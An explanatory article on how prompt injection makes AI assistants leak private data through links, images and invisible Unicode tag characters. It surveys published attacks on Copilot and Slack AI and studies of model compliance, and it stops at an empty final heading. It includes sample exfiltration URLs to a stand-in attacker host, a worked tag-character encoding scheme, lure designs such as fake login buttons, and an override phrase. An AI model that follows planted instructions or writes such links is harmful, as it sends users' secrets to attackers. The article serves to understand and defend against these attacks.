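# Data theft through links and invisible Unicode in AI assistants' answers

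## How a link can carry private data out of an assistant

AI assistants such as Microsoft 365 Copilot and ChatGPT answer questions using material they look up for the user, including email, chat messages, shared documents and web pages. Some of that material comes from strangers. Anyone can send the user an email, and that email can contain instructions for the assistant. If the assistant follows them, it can gather private data from elsewhere in the account and put it in the URL of a link in its answer. The link looks ordinary to the user, but opening it sends the whole URL, including the data, to the attacker's server.

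In security, exfiltration means moving private data to a place the attacker controls. In user-click exfiltration, the data leaves only when the user opens a link that the assistant displayed.

### Instructions inside the data

The attack begins with an indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker plants instructions in content that an assistant reads, and the assistant follows them as if its user had given them. Unlike in a direct injection, where the attacker types the hostile prompt, the person typing is the victim, who may have asked only for a summary. In the typical case that Microsoft describes, the application joins the text of a web page to the user's request and gives both to the model as a single input. The attacker can hide the instructions, for instance as white text on a white background, but visible instructions in a plain text file also work.

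SQL injection is a similar problem that older software has largely solved. An attacker types a database command into a field on a web page, and the database runs it. Parameterized queries prevent this by passing the command and the user's text to the database separately, so that it cannot interpret the text as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C (2025), a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, explains that this fix does not work for language models because a model takes in everything as one sequence of tokens (words and pieces of words) and predicts the next one. David C concludes that prompt injection may never be fully preventable in the way SQL injection is.

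Developers try to mark where text came from by wrapping it in role tags, which label one passage as the user's and another as a tool's output. They train models to give user text more authority. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) measured how much these tags affect the way a model internally represents text. They wrapped identical web text in different tags and trained simple classifiers on the model's internal activations, so the classifiers could learn only the effect of the tags. They then relabeled user messages from 200 real conversations as tool output. Because the wording had more influence than the tag, the classifiers for all four open models tested still assigned these messages a 76 to 88 percent probability of being user text, and never more than a 20 percent probability of being tool text.

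Ye and colleagues ran 1,000 attempts to make an agent upload a secret file while it summarized a web page. They kept the command fixed and varied the text around it, sometimes stating that what followed came from the user. The success rate rose from 2 percent when the command registered least as user text to 70 percent when it registered most.

Those classifier results come from models of 20 to 120 billion parameters, and resistance to crude attacks has clearly improved. In a separate test by the same researchers, a fake user command on a web page succeeded at most 2 percent of the time on every model but one. Forged reasoning in the model's own style raised the rate to between 56 and 70 percent. In June 2026 Anthropic reported that its Mythos 5 model had the best result yet on a prompt-injection benchmark from the security company Gray Swan. But a low success rate is not a security boundary,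 since an attacker can reword an email and send it again. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) similarly rates delimiters and role labels as useful engineering practice but not a hard security boundary.

### What an address sends

Suppose the attacker wants a login code, 481920, from the victim's inbox. A link that carries it could have this made-up address:

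`https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920`

The host, `files.example`, identifies the server, and the path, `/reports/q3`, identifies the page. Everything after the question mark is the query string, which passes extra values to the server. Legitimate sites often use query strings for search terms, page numbers and advertising tags, so a long one looks unremarkable.

When someone opens the link, the browser looks up the host, connects to it and sends a request that starts with the line `GET /reports/q3?ref=481920`. The server typically adds an entry like this to its log:

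`203.0.113.7 [05/Dec/2026:09:14:02] "GET /reports/q3?ref=481920" 404`

The log entry gives the visitor's network address, the time, the requested path and query string, and a status code. A status code of 404 means that the page does not exist, but the attacker still receives the login code because it arrived with the request. Using "https" does not help either, because it protects the request from eavesdroppers on the way, and the attacker is the recipient. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes the same mechanism and notes that websites commonly log the URLs that visitors request.

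The query string is the most convenient place for the data, but Microsoft also mentions the path and a subdomain (an extra label in front of the host name). Microsoft notes that an attacker can first encode the data in base64, a reversible scheme that turns text into a run of letters and digits. A user who inspected the address would then see something like a tracking code.

Most users would not examine the link's address, because it is hidden behind the link text. Language models usually write links in Markdown, a plain-text notation that an application turns into formatted text. When the model writes `[Q3 report](https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920)`, the user sees only the clickable words "Q3 report".

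### From planted text to log entry

Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, demonstrated the full attack against Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2024. His post *Microsoft Copilot* reproduces the planted text, which instructed Copilot, when asked for the document's key points, to find an email from the day before titled "secrets and codes", write its body into a link, and remind the user to click for details. Copilot ran the search without asking anyone. Rehberger also had it write the stolen text in Unicode tag characters, which most software does not display, so the text did not show in the link's visible address.

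The attack breaks down into six steps:

| Step | What happens | Where it happens |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Planted content | The attacker sends an email or shares a document, and the assistant reads it while working on a request | The user's mailbox or files, then the model's input |
| 2. Retrieval of private data | The model, following the planted text, searches for something the attacker wants | A tool call |
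| 3. Construction of the address | The model writes the data into a link | The text of the answer |
| 4. Display | The application turns the Markdown into clickable words | The application's display code |
| 5. Click | The user opens the link and the browser sends the request | The user's browser |
| 6. Log entry | The server records the address | The attacker's server |

A tool call is a structured request from the model, such as "search the mailbox for this phrase", which the surrounding software carries out. The software can first inspect the request, and refuse it or ask the user. The important tool call in this attack is the search in step 2. Step 1 may also involve one if the assistant has to look up the attacker's document, but the user wanted that lookup. There are no tool calls from step 3 onward. The model writes the link containing the stolen code as part of its answer, and the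 software handles it like any other text in the answer.

The attack doesn't need a search if the private data is already in the conversation, either because the user pasted it or because an earlier question brought it up. The planted text then only has to get the model to copy that data into a link's address.

Each step looks minor by itself, which affected how Microsoft first handled the problem. In January 2024 Rehberger reported only the invisible characters, and Microsoft closed the ticket a day later as low severity. In February he reported the complete chain, using sales figures as the stolen data, and Microsoft opened an internal case within three days.

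### Images load by themselves

An attacker can avoid depending on a click by using an image instead of a link. In Markdown, an exclamation mark in front of a link turns it into an image, which a browser fetches as soon as it appears on the page. The request has the same form and leaves the same log entry as one from a clicked link, but displaying the image is enough to send the data. This is zero-click exfiltration, in which software makes the request without any action by the user. Archestra's *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags* points out that the chat interface sends the data, so the model needs no tool for sending it.

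The image route became public first, in April 2023, when the software developer Simon Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection", publicized a demonstration by Roman Samoilenko. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) describes how Samoilenko had ChatGPT display a one-pixel image with chat data in its address. Samoilenko got the instructions for this into the chat through a web page that silently added them to any text a visitor copied from it.

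Vendors responded by restricting images. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft stopped Bing Chat from loading them in May 2023 using a Content Security Policy, a set of rules limiting which servers the browser can load a page's resources from. OpenAI followed in December 2023. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* found that ChatGPT's web version checked with an OpenAI server whether an image's address was safe before showing it, but the iPhone app still lacked the check. Willison reported that GitHub disabled images from untrusted domains in Copilot Chat.

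Rules that restrict which images a page may load do not restrict which links a user can click. Rehberger's 2024 attack used a link because Microsoft had already closed the image route he had reported the year before. A link is less reliable for the attacker, since the user may ignore it, but the planted text can dictate the words around the link, and those words appear in an answer from an assistant that the user chose to consult. Microsoft has since blocked some untrusted links as well.

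The fixes did not end zero-click attacks either. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes an attack in which Copilot displayed a small web page that loaded a font from Rehberger's server, with the stolen email in the font's address. Microsoft patched that in March 2026. On December 3, 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, found at the security company Cato Networks. One of them again used an image address, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), which dates the last of Microsoft's patches to November 15. Cato knew of no real attackers who had used any of the three.

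### Three conditions and a missing checkpoint

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, argues that an assistant is open to data theft when it has access to private data, takes in untrusted content (any text or image that an attacker could control), and can communicate externally in a way that could carry the data out. He counts a link offered to the user as external communication, just like a tool that contacts a server directly. His post lists 17 reports of such attacks on working products between April 2023 and June 2025, including one on Slack's AI assistant.

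Some of the three conditions are harder to remove than others. An email assistant is useless if it cannot read the user's mail, and not much better if it ignores mail from outsiders. Rehberger concludes that external communication is the only one of the three that anyone can realistically restrict in Copilot. Willison's list supports this, since vendors fixed almost all of those cases quickly, usually by blocking the channel that sent data out while leaving the injection possible.

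A standard design in computer security for enforcing a rule like this is the reference monitor, a component that checks every security-relevant action before it happens and that whatever it controls cannot bypass or alter. An operating system works roughly this way with files. A program cannot read the disk directly, so it must request files through the operating system, which checks the program's permissions first. The requirement that every access or action pass through such a check is called complete mediation. If any route avoids the check, an attacker will use it, however strict the check is on other routes.

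A monitor on an AI assistant's tool calls does not cover a link displayed in the answer or the user's click on it. The tool call is still the natural place for a monitor, because that is where the model's output turns into an action that ordinary software carries out. This fits David C's advice to rely on safeguards outside the model that constrain what the system can do. A monitor there could stop an assistant from emailing a login code to a stranger, because the request would contain both the recipient and the message. In Rehberger's attack, it would have detected only Copilot searching the user's own mailbox, which is what people use Copilot for. The link containing the stolen email was part of the answer, and the user's browser sent the request that delivered the data after the assistant had finished. Complete mediation would therefore need a further check between the written answer and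 the outgoing request. Whether any check there can be complete is an open question when the last step is a person's decision to open a link.

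## Attacks that put stolen data in an ordinary link

By June 2025, Willison had seen assistants in about a dozen products offer users a Markdown link with private data in its URL. Researchers have described two of these attacks in detail, one on Slack AI in 2024 and one on Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2025. Both vendors have since patched their products. Both attacks put the stolen data in the link's query string as ordinary letters and digits, whereas the Copilot attack that Embrace The Red demonstrated in 2024 used invisible characters.

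### Slack AI: a secret behind an error message

Slack is a workplace chat service that sorts messages into channels. Everyone in a company's workspace can read its public channels, but only a private channel's members can read it. Slack AI answers questions by searching everything the user can read, including public channels they have never joined. *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published by the security company PromptArmor in August 2024, explains how an attacker could use this search to steal a secret from a private channel.

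In PromptArmor's demonstration, the victim keeps an API key (a password-like string that lets software use a service) in a private channel with no other members. The attacker creates a public channel and posts one message there. Nobody else joins, and other people see the channel only if they search for it. Large workspaces have so many channels that one more is unlikely to attract attention.

The attacker's message opens with the name of the key that the victim is likely to ask for. It then instructs the model to answer with a loading error and a link. Because the attacker does not know the key, the link's address contains a dummy word that the model is instructed to replace with the real key.

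Later the victim asks Slack AI for the key. The search finds both the victim's own message and the attacker's, and Slack AI puts them into the model's context, the text the model works from when it answers. The model now has the key from one message and instructions from the other. It replies that there was an error loading the message and offers a link with the words "click here to reauthenticate". If the key were `k7Q2-9931`, the address behind those words would look like this made-up one:

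`https://attacker.example/?secret=k7Q2-9931`

When the victim clicks, the key arrives in the attacker's server log.

Slack's permissions worked as designed. The search ran on behalf of the victim, who was allowed to read both messages, and the attacker never gained access to the private channel. The attack only required the two messages to be in the same context.

The attack depends on the search finding the attacker's message, so the message's opening words mattered. *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier* (2026) calls retrieval the bottleneck of indirect prompt injection, and criticizes earlier experiments for testing what happens after a system retrieves the malicious text but not whether a natural question would retrieve it. An attacker therefore has to guess what people will ask for. PromptArmor thought a rough guess might be enough, because the victim's search also brought up messages about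 other API keys. Willison (2024) stressed in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* that the API key was only an example, and that the same trick could put other private details from Slack into a link.

Slack AI attaches numbered citations to its answers, but in the demonstration they failed to expose the attacker's message. The only citation pointed to the victim's own private channel. That was the correct source for the key, but the error message and the link came from the attacker's channel, which Slack AI did not cite. The attacker's message was also missing from the first page of ordinary search results, so a suspicious victim would have had to scroll to find it.

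PromptArmor did not establish why the citation was missing. In a second demonstration, the planted message targeted requests to summarize a manager's messages, and Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel. PromptArmor concluded that the citations were fairly random. A likely explanation is that the model picked its citations while writing the answer, since software that listed every retrieved message would have cited the attacker's message both times. If so, the citations were no more trustworthy than the rest of the answer.

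Even a complete citation might not have helped. When PromptArmor reported the problem, Slack's reviewers noticed a reference to a public channel in one of the videos and replied that Slack AI was right to show the information because it had been posted publicly. They apparently thought the secret came from the public channel, which had actually supplied the instructions.

Slack (2024) deployed a patch on August 20, the day the research became public, and reported no evidence of unauthorized access to customer data. It did not explain what the patch changed. Slack emphasized that the attacker needed an account in the same workspace. That may no longer have been true, because Slack AI had begun to draw on uploaded files and connected drives on August 14. If an employee downloaded a PDF with hidden instructions and uploaded it to Slack, the attack could have worked without an account. PromptArmor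 had finished its tests before the change and did not try this, but considered it highly likely to work.

### Microsoft 365 Copilot: emails in a login button

In October 2025 the security researcher Adam Logue published *Microsoft 365 Copilot Arbitrary Data Exfiltration via Mermaid Diagrams*, which describes an attack that began when a user asked Copilot to summarize an Excel spreadsheet. Mermaid is a tool that draws diagrams, such as flowcharts, from a short text description, and Copilot could display them in the chat. The description can include a link and styling, so a diagram can be a single box that looks like a button and opens a web address.

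BeyondMachines' *Microsoft 365 Copilot vulnerability enables data theft through malicious Mermaid diagrams* (2025) reports that the spreadsheet's first sheet contained believable financial figures and white text that directed Copilot to the second sheet. White text on the second sheet changed the task in stages, until Copilot was instructed to tell the user that the document was sensitive and required a login. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, Logue took inspiration from Microsoft's research on detecting "task drift", in which a model departs from what the user asked for.

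Copilot followed the instructions. It used its email search tool to fetch the user's recent company emails, listed their contents and converted the list to hexadecimal. Hexadecimal writes each character of plain English text as two characters from 0–9 and a–f, so the login code 481920 becomes `343831393230`. Like base64, it is easy to decode but hard to read at a glance. It also replaces spaces and line breaks, which a web address cannot contain directly, with letters and digits.

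The encoding doubles the length of the text, and Mermaid allowed only 200 characters per line, so a single line could hold at most 100 characters of email. The planted instructions told Copilot to split the encoded string into lines of at most 30 characters, with backslashes to join them. Each line then carried up to 15 characters of email, and the diagram displayed without errors.

The user saw a login button with a lock emoji. Clicking it sent the encoded emails to Logue's server, where he could decode them from the log. The diagram then turned into an iframe, which shows content from another site inside the current page. Logue had his server return a picture of the real Microsoft 365 login screen, so it looked as if the user was signing in. After several seconds the frame disappeared from the chat, which removed much of the visible evidence.

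Logue reported the attack on August 15, 2025. Microsoft had trouble reproducing it at first, confirmed it on September 8 and fixed it by September 26, according to Cyber Security News. The fix removed clickable links from Copilot's Mermaid diagrams. Like most such fixes, it blocked one way of sending data out but left the injection possible. BeyondMachines doubted that the patch covered every variation. Earlier, Mermaid diagrams in the code editor Cursor could leak data through remote images without a click.

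### How the two attacks differed

| | Slack AI | Microsoft 365 Copilot |
|---|---|---|
| Planted text | Message in a public channel with one member | White text on two sheets of a spreadsheet |
| Source of the data | A private message that the user had asked about | Recent emails that the user had not asked about |
| Encoding | None | Hexadecimal, in lines of up to 30 characters |
| Lure | A loading error and a link to reauthenticate | A notice that the document was sensitive, and a login button |
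| What the user could see | The key, in readable form, when hovering over the link | A button whose address held hexadecimal instead of readable text |

The source of the data affects how easily software could detect the theft. In the Slack attack, the assistant looked up exactly what the user wanted, so the search did not look suspicious. Copilot's email search was more suspicious because summarizing a spreadsheet does not normally require reading the user's mail. A program that compared each tool call with the user's request could have flagged that search.

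The encoding matters more to the user because it hides the stolen data. A Slack victim who hovered over the link could have seen their own key next to an unfamiliar domain, but in the Copilot attack the domain was the only readable clue.

An attacker can learn private information from a link whose address contains none of it. Willison's *Living off Microsoft Copilot* describes a demonstration in which hidden text in an email had Copilot search the user's files to find out whether Microsoft's quarterly earnings exceeded 53 billion dollars, then look up one of two web pages depending on the answer. If the user follows a link to that page, the attacker can learn the answer by seeing which page was visited. This reveals only one yes-or-no fact, but it could be valuable before an earnings announcement.

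### Why a fake obstacle makes a good lure

In both the Slack and Copilot attacks, the assistant withheld the answer and presented clicking a link as the way to get it. The user already wanted the key or the summary, so the attacker did not have to create interest in the link. Users have little reason to click a link for further reading when the assistant has already answered their question.

Expired sessions and repeated logins are also common in office software, and some of Microsoft's chatbots have login buttons. Datadog Security Labs' *CoPhish* (2025) examined Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building custom assistants, and found that its built-in "Login" button could redirect users to any address. Someone who has used a genuine login button in a chatbot may not find it odd when Copilot shows one above a spreadsheet summary.

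An obstacle also means the attacker doesn't have to predict the user's question. Attackers write the planted text in advance, so a false answer would have to fit whatever the user later asks, but a login request fits almost any question. *LoginTrap* (2026) tested this on web agents, AI systems that operate a browser for their users, by placing login prompts on the pages they visited. The attack succeeded 86 percent of the time on average across several models and types of website. The researchers suspected that a login would seem less necessary on information pages, where visitors have more varied goals, but the attack worked there too. The result shows that an attacker can reuse one lure across many tasks, but not how often people would fall for it, since the victims were agents.

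Someone who has just seen a loading error will not be surprised if clicking the link leads to another error or a second login screen. Logue exploited this with a picture of the Microsoft login page. An attacker could instead put a working form there to collect the user's password. In PromptArmor's second Slack demonstration, the link carried no stolen data but led to a phishing page.

### How readily models write an attacker's address

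These attacks work only if the model includes the attacker's URL in its answer. *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates* (Fogel, Cohen and colleagues, 2026) reports the highest measured rates of this, but its attacker held a stronger position than someone who plants text in an email. A chat template is a small program, packaged with a downloadable model, that arranges each conversation into the format the model expects. The attacker alters the template and republishes the model. When a user's question contains a certain phrase, in this test a request for references where relevant, the template adds an instruction to the system message telling the model to include a particular URL. Models give the system message the most authority, so the attack doesn't depend on the model mistaking outside content for a command.

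Fogel and colleagues tested 18 models from seven families:

| Form of the address | Average success rate |
|---|---|
| Plain, visible URL | 0.9 |
| Hidden in an HTML comment, which a browser does not display | 0.81 |
| Encoded in base64 | 0.67 |

Without the trigger phrase, no model produced the address. The encoded version worked mainly on larger models. The address was the same each time and contained nothing about the user, so these rates measure how often models include a link, not whether an attack could steal data with one. In a separate test, a poisoned template got a shopping agent to put the user's card number and other personal details into a web address in all four runs. That agent sent the request itself with a browser tool, so the user didn't have to click anything.

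The results suggest that once models treat an instruction as legitimate, an unfamiliar address does not stop them from following it. An attacker who uses indirect injection must first get them to treat the instruction that way, and success rates for this step vary enormously.

Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, studied instructions that people had placed on the web. They searched 1.2 billion URLs, added results from two other search services and confirmed about 15,000 cases. Most were crude, and 99 percent simply told the model to abandon its task. One of the ten most common templates told the model to send the user to a named domain, although all 1,262 copies came from a single site. The researchers then ran 5,200 trials in which 13 models summarized pages containing such instructions. Compliance peaked at 8 percent, for smaller models that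 received the page as plain text. It fell to between 0.2 and 1.1 percent when the input preserved the page's structure. These figures cover many kinds of instruction, including requests for random numbers, so they are only a rough guide to how models treat links.

More carefully worded attacks succeed far more often. *TopicAttack* (2025) placed an invented user-assistant conversation before the malicious instruction, so that the subject shifted gradually from the original text to the attacker's request. The attack succeeded more than 90 percent of the time in most cases, even with defenses in place. This test did not focus on links either, but Logue's spreadsheet also changed Copilot's task in stages. The low success rates for crude web text are therefore only limited reassurance against a determined attacker.

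In *Prompt-in-Content Attacks* (2025), Lian, Wang and colleagues placed one instruction in the middle of an otherwise harmless Word document, uploaded it to seven assistants through their normal websites and asked for a summary. The instruction told the assistant to recommend a web address instead of summarizing. Grok 3, DeepSeek R1, Kimi and Gemini 2.5 Flash recommended the address, while ChatGPT 4o, Claude Sonnet 4 and Perplexity did not. Grok, DeepSeek and Kimi also obeyed an instruction to claim that a format problem prevented them from processing the document, the kind of false error used against Slack AI. All seven assistants are now old, and Kimi sometimes gave different responses to identical tests, so the exact split matters less than the fact that such a simple instruction worked.

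To steal data, the attacker also needs the model to put private information in the link's address. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) scores this step separately. Its test plants an image and a link with placeholders for the user's email address and ID. If an agent includes them but doesn't replace the placeholders, the attack counts as half a success. The agent examined, AIRA, gave the planted image and link their own section in its report.

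Lian and colleagues got Grok 3 to complete the whole sequence. The user had typed a database password earlier in the conversation, and Grok had warned that it was weak and said it would not store or use it. The user then uploaded a document with hidden instructions and asked for a summary. Grok recommended a website for more complete information and put the password in the link's query string. The spaces in the surrounding text appeared as `%20` because of percent-encoding, which writes bytes that a web address cannot contain directly as a percent sign and two hexadecimal digits. The password remained readable. Grok also displayed the full address instead of hiding it behind link text, so an attentive user could have spotted the password without hovering over the link. Lian and colleagues used readable text for the demonstration and noted that an attacker could encode it to avoid suspicion.

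## How invisible Unicode characters hide data in a link

Encoding stolen data in hexadecimal or base64 makes it hard to read, but leaves a long string of letters and digits in the address that a careful user might notice. Unicode tag characters avoid this because most software doesn't display them. Security researchers call the technique ASCII smuggling. An attacker can use it to hide instructions from a human reader or to hide data in a model's output, though the link attack requires only the latter.

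Unicode is the standard that gives every character a number, called a code point. Code points are written in hexadecimal after "U+", so the digit 4 is U+0034. ASCII is an older set of 128 codes for English letters, digits and punctuation, and Unicode kept its numbering. The tag characters, in the block U+E0000 to U+E007F, are in effect an invisible second copy of ASCII.

### From language labels to flags

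The tag characters were originally meant to label the language of plain text, which has no markup like HTML's to hold such a label. Whistler and Adams (1999), in *Language Tagging in Unicode Plain Text*, proposed spelling out the label within the text, using characters that software could strictly separate from the content. Programs that supported the labels could use them, and others could skip them.

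The characters' designers hoped that few people would use them. In the IETF mailing-list thread *For v3*, someone involved in retiring the characters recalled that the designers had deliberately put them in a remote part of Unicode, where each one takes four bytes. They meant this as a hint that nobody really recommended the characters, although they were better than a rival proposal. The protocol that prompted the work never became popular, and the writer knew of no other protocol that adopted them.

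Whistler, Adams and colleagues (2010) formally retired the scheme in *Deprecating Unicode Language Tag Characters*, calling it "an idea whose time never quite came". They expected any effect of retiring it on internet security to be positive.

The Unicode Consortium, which maintains the standard, deprecated the tag characters in version 5.1 but never removed them, and it reversed the deprecation for most of them in version 8.0. Of the 97 characters, only the one that introduced a language label is still deprecated. In version 9.0, the Consortium gave the tag characters a new use in emoji. The flag of England, for example, is a black flag emoji followed by the tag versions of the letters "gbeng" and a closing tag. The flags of Scotland and Wales work the same way.

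A phone that does not support these sequences shows only the black flag. This follows a general rule in the Unicode Consortium's *Display of Unsupported Characters* that software should draw unsupported "default ignorable" characters as nothing, with no width. Without that rule, an old phone would show the Scottish flag as a black flag and a row of empty boxes. The same rule hides a stolen password encoded in these characters at the end of a web address.

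For software that does support tag sequences, the Unicode Consortium recommends marking a malformed sequence with a "missing emoji" symbol. Its examples of malformed sequences include tag characters with no emoji in front of them. Data hidden in a link normally takes this form, so software that followed the recommendation everywhere would reveal that the data was there.

The characters can also become visible by accident. In October 2024, Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* offered readers a text file containing two square brackets with twelve tag characters between them. Chrome on a Mac showed a pair of empty brackets. Several readers on Windows saw a string of accented letters and symbols, because their browsers had guessed the wrong text encoding and displayed each byte as a separate character. Mark Liberman, who wrote the post, thought it would be safer if applications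 always displayed the characters as gibberish. A web chat normally specifies its encoding, so an attacker's hidden text is less likely to be exposed this way there.

### Encoding a login code

The conversion from ordinary text takes one addition:

tag code point = U+E0000 + ASCII code

Take the login code 481920 from the earlier example. The ASCII code of the digit 4 is 34 in hexadecimal, so its tag character is U+E0034. A computer then has to store that number as bytes, usually in an encoding called UTF-8, which uses one byte for an ASCII character and four for a tag character. UTF-8 writes E0034 as 21 binary digits and divides them into groups of three, six, six and six:

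`011 100000 000000 110100`

UTF-8 puts `11110` in front of the first group of bits and `10` in front of each of the others. The resulting bytes are F3, A0, 80 and B4. Percent-encoding then writes each byte as three characters.

| Digit | ASCII code | Tag character | UTF-8 bytes | In the address |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | 34 | U+E0034 | F3 A0 80 B4 | `%F3%A0%80%B4` |
| 8 | 38 | U+E0038 | F3 A0 80 B8 | `%F3%A0%80%B8` |
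| 1 | 31 | U+E0031 | F3 A0 80 B1 | `%F3%A0%80%B1` |
| 9 | 39 | U+E0039 | F3 A0 80 B9 | `%F3%A0%80%B9` |
| 2 | 32 | U+E0032 | F3 A0 80 B2 | `%F3%A0%80%B2` |
| 0 | 30 | U+E0030 | F3 A0 80 B0 | `%F3%A0%80%B0` |

The six digits become six tag characters, which take up 24 bytes in UTF-8 and 72 characters once percent-encoded. To recover the code, the attacker reverses the percent-encoding and subtracts E0000 from each code point.

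Suppose the model adds the six tag characters to the end of `https://files.example/reports/q3`. If the chat displays the address as text, the user sees that address and nothing after it. When the user clicks, the browser sends the whole thing, and the attacker's server logs a request like this:

`"GET /reports/q3%F3%A0%80%B4%F3%A0%80%B8%F3%A0%80%B1%F3%A0%80%B9%F3%A0%80%B2%F3%A0%80%B0" 404`

### What hovering over the link shows

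When a user hovers over a link, the browser shows its address in a corner of the window, but only some browsers include the hidden part. In the Mozilla bug report *bottom-of-window URLs shown when hovering on a link don't percent-encode the same*, a Firefox user tried a sample link on Rehberger's blog. Firefox showed only `https://wuzzi.net/`. Chrome and Safari showed the same address followed by nine percent-encoded characters, which decode to "TrustNoAI".

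| Where the user or attacker looks | Login code as plain digits | Login code as tag characters |
|---|---|---|
| Chat, link behind the words "Q3 report" | Q3 report | Q3 report |
| Chat, address displayed as text | `.../q3?ref=481920` | `.../q3` |
| Hovering in Firefox | `.../q3?ref=481920` | `.../q3` |
| Hovering in Chrome or Safari | `.../q3?ref=481920` | `.../q3` and 72 characters of percent codes |
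| Server log | `/q3?ref=481920` | `/q3` and 72 characters of percent codes |

When a user hovers over a link, Firefox decodes percent-encoded text to make the address easier to read. As a side effect, this hides tag characters, which are invisible once decoded. The address bar keeps them percent-encoded, but a user who notices them there has usually opened the link already.

A Mozilla developer agreed that the hover text should match the address bar but gave the change a low priority, reasoning that hover text is trustworthy only on benign sites because a malicious page can falsify it. That reasoning applies poorly to AI assistants, where the chat page belongs to Microsoft or another legitimate company and the attacker controls only the link, so accurate hover text would help. The bug was still open in April 2026.

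Mozilla fixed a related problem in October 2025. *Status panel shows incorrect domain with certain bidi isolation characters* reports that some characters that control the direction of Arabic and Hebrew text could make a link appear to lead to a different domain. The fix keeps those characters percent-encoded in the hover text, but the list of characters it covers does not include tag characters. A developer had also tried reusing the address bar's code, which handled the test link equally well, but was unsure what else the change might affect.

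Chrome's behavior probably comes from a rule in the source code of Chromium (2020), the open-source project on which Chrome is based. Under this rule, Chromium converts addresses into readable form but leaves a list of characters percent-encoded because they could help someone disguise an address. The list includes the whole range from U+E0000 to U+E0FFF. A Chrome user who hovers over a link with tag characters therefore sees a stranger address than one with six plain digits, but can no longer read the data at a glance.

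### Why models can read tag characters

A tokenizer converts all the characters in a text, including those not displayed on the screen, into the tokens that a language model processes. In January 2024, the security researcher Riley Goodside showed that tag characters could therefore be used for prompt injection. According to Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, Goodside pasted harmless-looking text into ChatGPT, and the invisible instructions in it made ChatGPT generate an image.

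The table of bytes suggests why models can interpret the characters. Tokenizers commonly break rare characters into bytes, and all six tag digits share the first three bytes. Only the last byte changes, in the same order as the digits. Letters follow a similar pattern. A model that has learned ordinary ASCII therefore only has to make a simple substitution.

Cisco gives a similar explanation, which it credits to the researcher Rich Harang: the tokenizer separates the repeated tag part from the part that identifies the original character, and the model attends to the meaningful part. Embrace The Red suspected that the models' training data had also contained tag characters. Both explanations could be true, but some models may not be able to read the hidden characters, since tokenizers and training data differ.

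### How often models obey hidden text

*Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) has the most detailed measurements of whether models follow invisible instructions. The test reverses an ordinary CAPTCHA, which people can solve and machines cannot. Graves hid an instruction in each of 30 trivia questions to reply with a wrong answer, such as "VIOLET". A model that gave only the hidden answer had followed the instruction.

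Graves used two encodings, tag characters and zero-width binary. Zero-width binary represents each letter as eight binary digits, using two invisible characters, a zero-width space for 0 and a zero-width non-joiner for 1. "Reply VIOLET" is 12 characters long, including the space, so it takes 12 tag characters or 96 zero-width characters.

The models also received different amounts of help:

- With no hint, nothing told the model that the question contained hidden text.
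- With a code-point hint, the system message named the invisible characters and said that they encoded an instruction.
- With a full hint, the system message also gave the decoding rules.
- In a fourth condition, the model got the full hint, and the hidden text told it to ignore all previous instructions instead of simply asking for the word.

Adding an unaltered control version of each question brought the total to 270 cases. Graves ran them on five models from OpenAI and Anthropic, at least three times each, with and without a tool for running Python code, which produced 8,308 answers.

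| Model | Obeyed without tool | Obeyed with tool | Obeyed zero-width binary | Obeyed tag characters |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.8% | 49.2% | 27.5% | 22.5% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 6.7% | 51.1% | 18.2% | 43.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 16.9% | 71.2% | 41.5% | 55.0% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.1% | 1.6% | 1.5% | 0.1% |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.1% | 20.6% | 20.6% | 0.1% |

The two tool columns combine both encodings and all hint conditions, and the two encoding columns combine the runs with and without the tool.

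The Python tool made the largest difference. With it, a model could write a line of code that subtracted E0000 from each character's code or turned the binary digits back into letters, instead of having to recognize the hidden text unaided. But the tool did little without a hint that there was something to decode. Without a hint, models followed the hidden instructions in at most 1.1 percent of cases without the tool and in 0 to 11 percent with it. With both a hint and the tool, Claude Opus 4 followed instructions hidden in tag characters every time.

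GPT-5.2 showed the opposite pattern. With the tool, it followed a benign hinted instruction 69 to 70 percent of the time in zero-width binary and almost never in tag characters. Graves attributes such differences to tokenizers and training data, which is plausible but untested. Alternatively, OpenAI may have removed tag characters before they reached the model, in which case no tool could have decoded them. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* reports that a few unnamed vendors had introduced fixes for tag characters in their APIs, the interfaces through which other software uses a model.

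Telling the model to ignore its previous instructions lowered the rate from 32.0 to 23.9 percent for Opus 4 and from 11.8 to 6.1 percent for GPT-5.2, but raised it from 43.7 to 59.6 percent for Sonnet 4. The rate may have fallen for Opus 4 and GPT-5.2 because they had been trained to resist that familiar phrase.

The highest rates came from tests in which Graves put decoding hints in the system message, which someone who only sends an email cannot edit. Graves therefore treats the results with hints as a measure of what models can do, and the results without them as a measure of what they do on their own. An email can contain its own decoding instructions in ordinary text, though these would carry less authority than instructions in a system message. Graves did not test that case.

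The grading was also strict about wording. On the control questions, which contained no hidden text, Claude Haiku's accuracy fell from 82 to 62 percent when it had the tool. Graves thinks this was mostly because the automatic grader failed to match long answers. The same problem could have hidden some cases where a model obeyed the hidden text.

### What newer models do

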